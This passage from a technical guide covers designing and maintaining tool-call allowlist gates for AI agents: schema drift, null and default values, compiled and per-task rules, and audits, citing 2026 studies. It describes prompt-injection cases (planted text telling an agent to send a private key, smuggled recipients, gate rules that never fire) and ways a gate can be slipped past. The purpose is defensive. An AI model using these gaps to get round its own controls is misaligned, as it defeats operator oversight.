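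Protocol Buffers, Google's format for messages between programs, is more tolerant. According to its *Language Guide (proto 3)*, a program with an old definition ignores new fields when it reads a message but keeps them when it writes the message out again. kmcd.dev's *protobuf unknown fields* says that early versions of proto3 dropped unknown fields and that version 3.5 began keeping them.

Protocol Buffers' tolerance of unknown fields lets a company update hundreds of programs one at a time without losing data. The same tolerance is dangerous in a gate, which would ignore an unknown field such as `also_post_to` and then pass it to a tool that acts on it. The format's JSON version is a better choice because *ProtoJSON Format* specifies that programs should reject unknown fields by default, although a developer can switch this off. However, the JavaScript library protobuf.js discards them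 by default.

### A new option in an old argument

Suppose a file-sharing tool has an argument `visibility` with two options, `private` and `public`. An engineer writes a rule that holds the call for a person to review if the value is `public` and otherwise allows it. The developer later adds `partners`, which shares the file with every partner company. The rule allows calls with this new value because it isn't `public`.

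The engineer should name each permitted option and refuse the rest:

```
private          allow
public           hold for a person
anything else    refuse
```

Some programming languages can also check that code handles every option in a definition (exhaustive matching). Protocol Buffers' guide warns that adding an option stops such code from compiling, and that Google may avoid adding options to public messages for that reason. This is useful for a gate because nobody can build it with the new definition without first deciding how to handle `partners`. A gate that is already running doesn't get this check, so it still needs the last line.

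The format can even hide the new option from the gate. According to Protocol Buffers' *Enum Behavior*, if a program reads an option that isn't on a "closed" list, the library reports the field as unset and returns the default. If the default is `private`, the gate allows the call, and the library then writes the new option, `partners`, back into the message for the tool. The language guide recommends making the default an option that means only "unspecified", which a gate can refuse. A Rust library documented on Docs.rs has a setting that replaces unknown options with the default instead of reporting an error, which makes the setting unsafe in a gate.

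### Renamed and plural arguments

If a developer renames `recipient` to `recipients`, a gate that checks `recipient` only when it is present will skip the check. A gate that requires `recipient` and refuses unknown arguments will block the call, because `recipient` is missing and `recipients` is unknown.

A change is harder to handle when an argument keeps its name but starts accepting a list. In Protocol Buffers' binary format, a program that expects one piece of text and receives several takes the last. If a hijacked agent lists a thief's address first and an approved customer's second, a gate that still expects one address checks only the customer's, and the tool emails both. The gate should refuse any value that isn't of the type in its rule. Once the operator has approved lists, the gate should check every item.

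A gate also has to convert field names to one spelling before comparing them, because ProtoJSON parsers accept both `also_post_to` and `alsoPostTo` for the same field.

### Changed defaults

An identical call can also have a different effect in a new version of a tool. In *When Valid Tool Calls Change Meaning*, Kim and Kang (2026) tested GitHub's MCP server with a call that specified only a new repository's name. Version 1.3.0 requested a public repository from GitHub, and version 1.4.0 requested a private one.

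The update was an improvement, but operators sometimes return to an old version or run both for a while. The researchers put two old and two new copies of the server behind a program that distributed calls at random. Whenever a call written for the new version reached an old copy, the result was a request for a public repository. A gate can't detect this from the call. Stating `private = true` kept the repository private in both versions, so an operator who requires an explicit publishing mode should also require explicit values for any other arguments that matter.

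Waiting for approval gives a tool's defaults more time to change. In another test, GPT-5.6 Sol wrote 12 calls that left out the recipient, and the tool's default recipient changed while the calls waited for approval. All 12 went to the new default. An approval system that runs exactly the call the owner saw wouldn't prevent this.

New arguments also have defaults. If `also_post_to` defaults to every connected site, it causes the same problem as WordPress.com's `publicize`, and somebody has to add an explicit "nowhere" to the rule.

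An explicit value works only if the server reads it. One release of Azure's MCP server added an option to switch off public network access, but Kim and Kang's checker couldn't establish that passing it had any effect in earlier releases. In Protocol Buffers, some fields don't record whether the sender set them, so an explicit `false` looks the same as no value. The Protocol Buffers guide recommends marking fields `optional`, which preserves the difference.

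### New tools and old wildcards

Suppose an operator permits `blog_*` because the server has two tools, `blog_search` and `blog_save_draft`. If an update adds `blog_delete_all`, the old rule permits that too. Such additions aren't rare, since the releases that Ameur and colleagues compared added 907 tools. Listing each permitted tool by its exact name keeps the rule from covering new ones.

Patterns can also be too broad when first written. JSON Schema's guide warns that its patterns for property names match anywhere in the name unless the engineer marks the beginning and end, so `p` matches `apple`. If a tool rule matched names the same way, permitting `draft` would also permit `publish_draft`.

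Allowlisting a tool by its exact name doesn't block new functions added to that tool. *The Interplay of Harness Design and Post-Training in LLM Agents* (2026) tests agents on a schema that merges several tools into one and selects among their functions with an `action` argument. A company might approve `manage_posts` when it can only list and save posts, then find that an update lets it accept `action = "delete"`. The rule has to list the permitted actions as well as the tool name.

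### Missing, null and empty values

An argument can be missing, null (explicitly given no value) or empty, and programs treat these cases differently. JSON Schema distinguishes null from a missing argument, while in ProtoJSON, null and an empty list both leave the field unset. A gate could therefore accept null as harmless, and the tool could then apply its default. In 21 of the 580 compatible changes that Ameur and colleagues studied, an argument began to accept null.

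*AgentTrustCI* (Gupta, 2026) presents a Java tool with two conventions that would be risky in a gate. The tool tests agents before release by checking recordings of their runs. A policy check covers which tools and arguments the agent used, a second check compares the agent's answer with what the tools returned, and a third checks the order of the steps.

If the list of allowed tools is empty, the policy check permits every tool that isn't on a separate list of forbidden ones. If a rule lists the permitted options for an argument, the check compares the value with them only when the value isn't null. The engineer has to mark the argument as required as well:

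| Value of `visibility` | Options listed | Options listed, argument required |
|---|---|---|
| Missing | Pass | Fail |
| Null | Pass | Fail |
| Empty text | Fail | Fail |
| `partners` (unlisted) | Fail | Fail |
| `private` (listed) | Pass | Pass |

Gupta wrote 55 test cases, 30 with faulty runs and 25 with valid ones. In one faulty run, an agent closes a support ticket when the user asked it to search. The three checks together judged all 55 cases correctly. Each check alone judged 35 correctly, because it accepted the valid runs but caught only the ten faults written for it. No live model produced the runs, and Gupta says the results show coverage of this test suite, not accuracy in production.

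The published list of fault types includes missing arguments and invalid options, but not an empty tool list or a null option. One valid case contains an extra argument that the rule neither requires nor forbids, and the tool accepts it by design. This avoids false alarms in a test suite, but a gate built the same way would let `also_post_to` through.

Treating an empty list as "no restriction" is convenient for a test author who doesn't care which tools the agent uses. In a gate, the same convention would let the agent use almost anything once an operator deleted the last entry to stop it. In Kodathala's gateway, by contrast, an empty list of web addresses blocks every fetch. *Can Agents Trust Their Skills?* (2026) likewise uses an empty allowlist in its restrictive configuration for OpenClaw, an agent program.

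The convention for empty lists matters most when rules fail to load. The same paper found that Kimi Code CLI, a coding agent, accepts deny rules in its settings but has no code that loads them at startup, so it checks calls against an empty deny list, which forbids nothing. If an allowlist failed to load and an empty list meant "refuse everything", the agent would stop working and somebody would notice.

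An even safer option is to write `tools = []` for none and `tools = any` for all, and to have the gate refuse to start if the line is missing. *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents* (2026) describes a similar check that reports a misconfigured agent as an error during installation, before the agent can run.

### Pinning a schema

An operator can catch visible changes by pinning the schema, which means storing a fingerprint of the approved version and suspending the tool when its schema no longer matches. But this also suspends the tool when a change makes it safer or, if the fingerprint covers descriptions, when someone corrects a typo in one.

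Ameur and colleagues developed a rule that asks for approval only if an update lets an argument take a value it couldn't take before. Let V(a) be the set of values that argument a can take, counting "missing" as a value. The rule accepts an update without asking if, for every argument,

V_new(a) ⊆ V_old(a)

Before the update, `publish` had no `also_post_to` argument. Now that argument can contain any text, so the rule prompts for approval. If a developer removed `public` from the options for `visibility`, the rule would accept the change without a prompt.

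Checking arguments one at a time can miss a newly allowed combination. Suppose a deletion tool requires either `id` or `full_path`, and an update to the tool removes that requirement. Either argument could already be omitted, but now a call can omit both. SchemaCaps therefore asks about any schema change if the old schema links arguments in this way.

The researchers counted how often each rule would have asked about existing tools in releases from January 2025 to September 2026:

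| Rule | Requests for approval | Compatible changes that widened a tool without a request |
|---|---|---|
| Pin the whole definition | 2,004 | 0 |
| Pin the input schema | 1,197 | 0 |
| Ask only if old calls would break | 617 | 412 |
| SchemaCaps | 645 | 0 |

Under every rule, operators also receive requests about the 907 new tools. SchemaCaps would reduce an operator's requests by nearly half compared with pinning the input schema, but its software is complicated. In a synthetic test, an earlier version silently accepted 27 of 330 widening changes, a fault the researchers have since fixed. They also acknowledge that 645 requests are enough to encourage careless approval.

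Ameur and colleagues surveyed eight products and could determine the behaviour of six, none of which requires new approval when a tool's input schema widens. VS Code, for example, ties approvals to the tool's name, so they remain valid after the change. The official MCP registry doesn't keep versions of tool definitions, according to *Same Name, Different Server* (2026), so an operator needs to keep a separate copy of each approved schema.

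A pinned schema can't reveal a change in the code behind it. Kim and Kang found two releases of a Git server with the same relevant schema. The older one could be exploited to create a file, and the newer one rejected the same call. Pinning the server's version would catch this difference, but not a change in an outside service the server relies on. In *ProbeID* (2026), seven tools behaved differently in repeated tests over several weeks while every server's recorded version stayed the same.

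Strict pinning also stops legitimate work. Kim and Kang tested six calls that were waiting when the server's version changed. Under the new version, three would still have created a private repository, and three would have created a public one. Pinning each call to its exact version stopped all six, and approving the whole new version let all six run. Their system works out what each call would do in the new code, and let through only the three safe ones. But it needs a specialist's profile of each tool, and three of the 32 releases they tested had changed too much for the profiles to work.

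### Updating in stages

An operator can avoid many of these interruptions by having the gate give the model its own description of `publish`, containing only the arguments and options the gate's rules permit. The agent then has no reason to try `also_post_to`, and its old calls keep working after a compatible update. *A Policy Profile for Croissant* (2026) generates tool schemas from the policy, so nobody has to copy limits by hand. The gate still checks each call, because a stored copy of the schema may be out of date.

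Renamed arguments need more care because calls in the old form can fail. In the *Interplay* paper's tests, such calls fail with "Invalid tool format" even when the operation is the same. Protocol Buffers' guide to renaming an option avoids these failures by having developers first update every program to accept both names, then switch to writing the new one, and remove the old name last. A gate can likewise accept both argument names during the change if it applies the same rule to each and rejects calls that contain both. If calls set a brand-new argument explicitly, they have to start when the server changes, because the old version may reject it.

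Gupta suggests testing old and new expectations side by side during such a change, and warns against automatically replacing them with whatever the agent now does. The tests should include calls that ought to succeed. *Permission Denied* (2026), which evaluates coding agents under tight restrictions, runs probes before each agent starts. They check that forbidden operations and attempts to get around the restrictions fail, and that permitted operations still work.

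For the examples above, an operator could run these calls against a test copy of the server after every update:

```
an approved article, also_post_to = nowhere   allow
the same article, also_post_to missing        refuse
the same article, also_post_to = null         refuse
the same article to "attacker.net"            refuse
the same article with an invented argument    refuse
a file with visibility = "partners"           refuse
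an email whose recipient is a list            refuse
a call to blog_delete_all                     refuse
an approved article, with an empty allowlist  refuse
```

A broken gate that refused everything would still pass eight of the nine tests and fail only the first, so the first test matters as much as the others.

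## Writing the list and keeping it current

An operator can write an allowlist's entries by hand, compile them from a written policy, have a model generate them for each task, or infer them from logs of the agent's past calls. These methods differ in who can introduce an error and when the error becomes apparent.

| Source of entries | Who can introduce an error | When the error shows |
|---|---|---|
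| Written by hand | The person who writes them | A missing entry at the first refusal, a broad one at an audit or after an accident |
| Compiled from a policy | The policy's author, or the model that translates it | Some errors in checks before use, others not until an audit |
| Generated for each task | A user with a vague request, or the model | During that task |
| Learned from logs | Anyone who influenced the agent's past calls, including an attacker | A missing entry at the first refusal, a recorded mistake perhaps never |

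### Entries written by hand

Someone who knows a company's suppliers can write a good payment list in an afternoon, but rules with exceptions are harder to write. *NOMOS* includes a test in which an agent serves airline customers under a written policy that forbids changes to basic economy flights but allows a change of cabin on the same flights. The developers' hand-written rule blocked both.

A second set of rules, compiled by software from the same policy, contained the same mistake, so comparing the two sets didn't reveal it. A separate model exposed it by checking individual refusals against the full policy. The developers ran a similar test with a shop, and an audit of 160 calls from the two tests found that the shop's hand-written rules had missed a refund to the wrong card. Someone other than the person who wrote the entries should therefore check them against the policy and some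 real calls.

### Compiling a written policy

Many companies already have written rules on payments and refunds. The compiler in *NOMOS* turns a document like this into rules for a gate in four steps:

1. Ordinary code splits the document into clauses.
2. A language model translates each clause into candidate rules, and does so five times.
3. Ordinary code repairs or rejects faulty candidates, then keeps those that appeared in most of the five attempts.
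4. Ordinary code saves the remaining rules, each with the sentence it came from, and reports every repair and rejection.

For each rule, the model picks a condition from a fixed vocabulary, such as "the recipient is unknown", and names the tools the rule should cover. It doesn't write program code. A person has to prepare the vocabulary once for each kind of work. After that, the gate makes its decisions without a model.

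The checks in the third step caught a rule that would have stalled every conversation. The shop's policy required the agent to authenticate customers at the start of a conversation. The model turned this into a rule that blocked every tool, including the two used for authentication, until the agent had authenticated the customer. The software detected that these two tools were the only way to satisfy the rule and exempted them.

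The software found structural faults like this in 37% of 79 candidate rules for the airline and 13% of 53 for the shop. It ended up with ten rules for the airline and five for the shop. In a separate experiment with all the checks switched off, 8 of 14 airline rules and 3 of 5 shop rules could not work. A larger commercial model also produced faulty rules, so a better translator doesn't remove the need for checks.

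With the gate, the share of the airline agent's changes that broke the policy clauses the developers could measure fell from 66.3% to 2.6%. For the shop, it fell from 30.8% to 6.9%. The airline agent made a third as many changes with the gate, but it passed 47.6% of its runs, compared with 39.2% without the gate and 42.8% with the hand-written rules. The developers claim only that the compiled rules are not significantly worse than the hand-written ones.

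Most of the remaining violations happened because the compiler had missed a clause or left a tool out of a rule. This gate permits any call that no rule blocks, so, as with any blocklist, a missing rule triggers no warning. The developers have published their rules but not their software, so outsiders can't repeat the compilation.

### The rule on recipients

The developers also tested the compiler on AgentDojo's four groups of tasks: banking, travel, office work and the workplace chat program Slack. AgentDojo has no written policies, so they wrote a page of policy for each group. They knew what the attacks were aimed at, so the results may be better than an ordinary company's policy would produce.

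One condition in their vocabulary, `recipient_unknown`, is true if the user hasn't named the recipient and the account has no past transaction with them. It reads only an argument called `recipient`. The compiler attached it to several tools that have no such argument, including an email tool that uses the plural:

```
recipient_unknown reads:   recipient
send_email accepts:        recipients, subject, body, …
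in common:                 nothing
```

When the gate checked an email, it found no `recipient` and treated the condition as false. The rule was a prohibition, so the gate allowed the email. The rule on `send_email` looked sensible in the rule file, but it could never block anything. In the Slack tasks, 15 of 105 attacks succeeded through such a rule. In the office tasks, five of the six rule-tool pairings were inactive, and attacks succeeded about as often as with no gate.

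The developers added a check that compares the arguments a condition reads with the arguments each tool accepts. If the condition and the tool have no arguments in common, the software substitutes a broader condition, `target_not_user_named`, which also covers channels, web addresses and files. If it has no suitable substitute, it drops the pairing of that condition with that tool. The check uses only the names of the arguments, so it needs no test runs.

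The repair stopped all 15 Slack attacks, but it also reduced the agent's completion rate on legitimate Slack tasks from 57.1% to 14.3%. The table gives the results for the repaired rules. AgentDojo counts some attacks as successful even though no harmful call ran.

| Tasks | Attacks that succeeded, no gate | With the gate | Legitimate tasks completed, no gate | With the gate |
|---|---|---|---|---|
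| Banking | 46.5% | 0.0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Office work | 7.3% | 0.0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |

The gate caused a drop of 76.2 percentage points on Slack because the agent finds most of its targets while working. A user might ask it to summarise an article that Bob posted and send the summary to the team. The agent learns the article's address from Bob's message, and it would learn an attacker's address in the same way. A rule that allows only targets the user named blocks both addresses.

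Banking users mostly name the payee or pay someone they have paid before, so the rule rarely blocks a payment they want. The small loss on travel tasks is partly due to a weak rule that let one attack through, because it allowed the agent to create a calendar event as long as the user had asked for some change. With so few tasks, the losses on banking and travel could also be due to chance.

For workplace chat, a standing list of the company's own channels might be a better rule than requiring the user to name each one. An attacker could still choose among those channels, and the developers didn't test this option.

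### A list made from the user's request

*ClawGuard* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026) has the agent's own model write a list for each task. The model uses only the user's request and writes the list before the agent calls any tool, so text planted in a webpage can't influence it. The user can edit the proposed rules before they take effect. A fixed set of base rules, such as a ban on reading stored credentials, overrides anything the model or the user adds.

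In the paper's example, a user asks for a summary of three blog posts, saved in a reports folder. The list permits the page with the posts, the reports folder, and the tools for fetching, reading and writing. It forbids shell commands. One of the posts contains an instruction to use a shell command to send the user's private key to a stranger. The gate refuses the command both because the task's list forbids shell commands and because the base rules protect the folder with the key.

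If a call matches neither a permission nor a prohibition, the gate holds it for the user to approve or reject. It blocks the call if the user doesn't answer in time.

The researchers tested this with five models. The largest gains came against attacks hidden in tool descriptions or skill files, which are instructions that extend what an agent can do. On three benchmarks of these attacks, the average share stopped rose from 56.7% to 86.7%, from 62.1% to 89.5%, and from 75.9% to 94.2%. The models already resisted at least 92.8% of the attacks in ordinary web and file content. The paper's introduction reports a perfect score on those attacks with the gate, but its results include 99.1% and 99.8% for two of the models on one benchmark.

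Agents kept 87.4% of their normal task success when the gate refused every held call, and 95.1% when a user could approve up to three. The 87.4% figure is fairer to compare with the attack results, because the gate also refused every held call in those tests, whereas a user who can approve calls might approve a bad one.

Success fell most on web tasks, because the agent often needs pages that the request doesn't mention. With no approvals, agents kept 78.5% of their success on these tasks. The loss also varied by model. Under the strict setting, GPT-5.4 lost 8.1% of its task success and DeepSeek-V3.2 lost 21.6%, probably because weaker models write less precise rules.

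Some attacks need no forbidden call. One skill file told the agent to give websites about sustainable energy a high score without reviewing them. The agent could do this within its permissions, and the attack worked on most of the models.

### When the task names no destination

The request often doesn't mention a destination. *Environment Steering* (2026) handles this differently for payments and emails than for web addresses. Summers, Raghunath and colleagues had Claude Opus 4.8 write rules for each task, using a few examples they had corrected by hand.

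Suppose the user asks an agent to buy a smart watch. The agent can pay at the shop's checkout, but it also has a tool for bank transfers, and the request names nobody who should receive one. The model's instructions tell it to write this rule, in simplified form:

`send_money: recipient = no_authorized_destination`

The right-hand side is a placeholder that matches no real account, so the software blocks every transfer. The same method blocks emails when the task doesn't include a recipient. If the user tells the agent to pay a bill on a website, the rule instead requires the account number to appear on the page the agent read, and a model checks that page for planted instructions.

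For web addresses, the model writes a rule only if the request names a site, because following links is a normal part of web tasks. This keeps the agent useful, but the exception also covers a tool that submits forms and another that opens links that can trigger an action. The instructions leave unrelated sites to a separate check that relies partly on a model. An agent with an open-ended request, such as the one that sent the false tip in Philadelphia, could therefore submit a form without breaking any rule on the list.

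The rules also leave `cc` and `bcc` unchecked. The software can't handle lists of addresses in those arguments, and a rule on either one would make the software block every email. If the user asks the agent to email a colleague, planted text could cause the agent to copy in a stranger. An operator could prevent this by giving the agent an email tool without these two arguments.

With Qwen3 235B as the agent, the system completed 61% of the AgentDyn tasks and no attack succeeded. Nine other defences completed fewer tasks. The lists are only part of the reason, because AgentDyn often puts the attack in the same document as information the agent needs, and the system relies on a model to spot those attacks. A stronger model than the agent also wrote the rules, using examples for the same benchmark. Across four benchmarks, the average attack success rate fell from 30–74% to 0.2–14%. Kimi K2.5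 completed fewer AgentDojo tasks than before because its rules were too strict.

The form of the refusal had a large effect on task success. Success fell by 36.2% when a refusal ended the run, fell by 10.5% when the agent received only a general message about breaking a policy, and rose by 6.5% when the message explained the rule and named the permitted sources. Attacks almost never succeeded in any of the three cases.

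A mistake in a list written for a single task disappears when the task ends, although the model may make it again next time. Vague requests are the main difficulty. *NOMOS* reports that 16 of 288 attacks succeeded against Progent when a model wrote the list for each banking task. Twelve of the successful attacks were on the same two requests, one of which was to pay a bill "like last month". Neither request included an account number, so the list couldn't restrict the payment to the right account.

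### Learning from logs

An operator can also permit whatever the agent has done before, as Agent-Sentry's learned list does. This takes little effort and reflects the operator's actual work, but the logs also contain mistakes. If Anthropic had built a list at the end of August from every call that nobody had questioned, it would have included the Philadelphia police form, because the company hadn't yet found the false tip.

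Logs also miss legitimate actions that are rare. Suppose a company pays each of 100 suppliers twice a year on average, at irregular times. The chance that a particular supplier appears in a log of T days is about

1 − e^(−2T/365)

A 30-day log would include about 15 of the 100 suppliers, a 90-day log about 39, and a full year's log about 86. Some of the most important actions, such as replacing a leaked key, may not appear. The operator has to add the missing suppliers and actions from other records, such as supplier contracts and emergency procedures.

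An attacker may be able to put an entry in the log. The banking rule in *NOMOS* permits payments to anyone in the account's transaction history, and its developers warn that a thief could send the company a small payment to become a known payee. AgentDojo doesn't include this attack, but the tests showed that a learned list can permit the wrong payment. In 8 of 288 attacked runs, the agent responded to planted text by paying somebody already in the history. With a second model, this happened in 11 of 140 runs and moved $41,250.

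It is safer to use logs only to suggest entries, so that a person can approve each one. The software can ignore incoming payments and any call from a run under attack.

### Observing before enforcing

A new list will have gaps, whatever its source. An operator can find many of them by having the gate record which calls it would refuse while still letting them through. Companies have long done this with lists of programs allowed to run on their computers. The US National Institute of Standards and Technology's guide to these lists, SP 800-167 (2015), recommends testing in a monitoring mode and introducing enforcement in phases. Microsoft's AppLocker, which arrived with Windows 7, has an audit mode that lets administrators see which programs would break the rules before blocking any.

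Observing irreversible actions without blocking them is risky because a bad payment still goes through. During the observation period, the operator should have a person approve each irreversible call, or run the agent against a test copy of the service. The gate's log then shows where the list differs from the reviewer's decisions.

Before using a new set of rules, *NOMOS* checks it against recordings of past runs by an unrestricted agent. It counts how often each rule would have refused a call in a run that succeeded, and flags any rule that would have refused at least 90% of the calls to a particular tool.

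This caught a serious mistake in rules for a phone company. The policy required the agent to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment. The compiled rule instead blocked payment requests while a bill was overdue. In the recordings, it would have blocked 47 of 49 legitimate requests. The same condition controlled the tool for restoring a customer's phone line, where it would have blocked none of the 44 calls to that tool. The operator could therefore remove the rule for payment requests and keep it for line restoration.

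A replay can't test a rule on a tool that the agent never used. It also can't show what the agent would have done after a refusal, since the recording continues regardless. The observation period should include at least one month-end and any other busy time that the operator can wait for. Enforcement can then begin with the tools where a wrong refusal does little harm.

### Reviewing refusals and adding entries

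Once the gate is enforcing the list, somebody has to read its refusals. Some will have blocked mistakes or attacks, and others will have blocked legitimate actions that are missing from the list. The number of refusals is a poor way to tell them apart, because an agent can repeat a bad call many times. If the software added every account that the gate had refused three times, a thief could get an account onto the list by sending three invoices.

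Each new entry should record who is responsible for it, why it exists and when it ends:

```
tool       send_money
recipient  DE89…  (Harbour Printing)
limit      500 USD, once a month
owner      accounts manager
reason     printing contract, account confirmed by phone
added      12 October 2026
expires    12 October 2027
last used  (the gate fills this in)
```

The owner should be someone who would know if the company stopped using the printer. A job title works better than a person's name, because people leave. If the company abolishes the job, somebody has to take over its entries or let them lapse.

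When an entry expires, the gate blocks the payment until the owner renews the entry. This applies the principle behind temporary grants to the permanent list. The owner needs a warning a few weeks ahead, or an expired entry will stop an urgent payment. If hundreds of entries expire on the same day, the owner will probably renew them all without reading them, so it helps to spread the expiry dates over the year.

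Some additions can't wait for a full review. During an outage, an engineer may need the agent to restart a server that isn't on the list. An entry that expires after an hour is safer than a permanent one that the engineer intends to remove later. The agent should never be able to edit the list, even by proposing an entry that takes effect automatically.

### Removing entries and testing changes

An entry the company doesn't use may still help an attacker. The gate can report entries that no call has matched for six months so that the owner can decide whether to remove them. Some rarely used entries are still necessary, such as those for paying annual taxes or replacing a leaked key. If the owner is unsure about an entry, the gate can hold matching calls for a person to review instead of refusing them.

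Before any change takes effect, the operator can run recorded calls through the old and new lists and compare the decisions. Most will be the same, and somebody should explain every difference:

| Old list | New list | What to find out |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse | Allow | Whether the company wants this action |
| Allow | Refuse | Who still needs this action |

If an editor accidentally shortened the printer's account number to `DE*`, the list would permit any German account. The comparison would reveal this only if the recordings included a refused payment to another German account. The operator therefore also needs invented calls, including known attacks and combinations of values that the list shouldn't permit. The recordings should include each tool's schema version, so that an update to a tool isn't mistaken for an effect of the new list.

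The gate in *NOMOS* also repeats most of its structural checks whenever it loads a rule file, which catches some mistakes in entries that people have edited by hand. But its check for rules that can never be satisfied looks at each rule separately. If one rule blocks tool A until the agent has used tool B, and another blocks tool B until it has used tool A, both rules pass the check even though the agent can never use either tool. Replaying a few ordinary tasks would reveal the problem.

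### Entries that change their meaning

An entry can become dangerous even if nobody edits it. If a company lists a supplier's domain and the supplier goes out of business, the registration eventually lapses and anyone can buy the domain. In 2025, security researchers bought an expired domain that Salesforce's AI agent software still trusted and showed that an attacker could use it to collect customer data.

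Email addresses have the same weakness. A company may give a former employee's address to a new employee with the same name. If a supplier's domain lapses, whoever buys it can receive mail sent to any address on it, including password-reset emails.

People also sell social media accounts and hand over software projects. Listing an account by its internal ID doesn't help after a sale, because the ID usually stays with the account. The agent would keep messaging the same account, and a different person would read the messages.

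In AppLocker, an administrator can identify a program by its location, its publisher or a fingerprint of the file. A location rule permits whatever program is there now, so what it permits can change even when the rule doesn't. A fingerprint rule always refers to the same file, but the administrator has to replace it after every update. A publisher rule covers future versions but relies on the publisher to keep its signing key safe.

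The gate's records are of little help here, because calls to the new owner succeed just as calls to the old one did. The operator has to check the entries against outside information. For a domain, software can look up the registration date and suspend the entry if that date is later than the approval. For an employee, the entry can refer to the staff directory, so that it ends when the person leaves. For a bank account, somebody can call the supplier on a known number.

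Regular renewal limits the damage if the owner actually checks the entry each time. If an account changes hands at a random time, the company would send payments or data to the wrong person for about six months on average with yearly checks and about six weeks with quarterly checks. An operator may want quarterly checks for accounts that receive money or private data and yearly checks for the rest.

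### What to measure

The rate of wrongful refusals is the most direct measure of how much the list obstructs legitimate work. If the gate refused 30 of 3,000 legitimate calls in a month, the rate is 1%. The operator should calculate it separately for each tool, since the average can be low even when the gate refuses a fifth of legitimate calls to a payment tool. Repeated attempts at the same task should count once.

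The time it takes to add an entry affects how people treat the list, and the slowest cases matter more than the average. If adding a new supplier takes three days, employees will start asking for broader entries or paying the bill some other way.

The share of entries that no call has matched for six months shows how much of the list may be out of date. The number of permitted combinations of account, destination, content type and mode shows how much the list allows. The publishing agent described earlier was meant to have four combinations, but separate lists permitted 108. A sudden jump in the number of permitted combinations usually means somebody has added a wildcard or merged rules carelessly.

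The first three measures alone could badly mislead an operator. Replacing the whole list with a single entry that permits everything would eliminate wrongful refusals, waits for new entries and unused entries. Only the number of permitted combinations would get worse. It also helps to have a person review a random sample of the calls that the gate allowed, because nobody complains about those.
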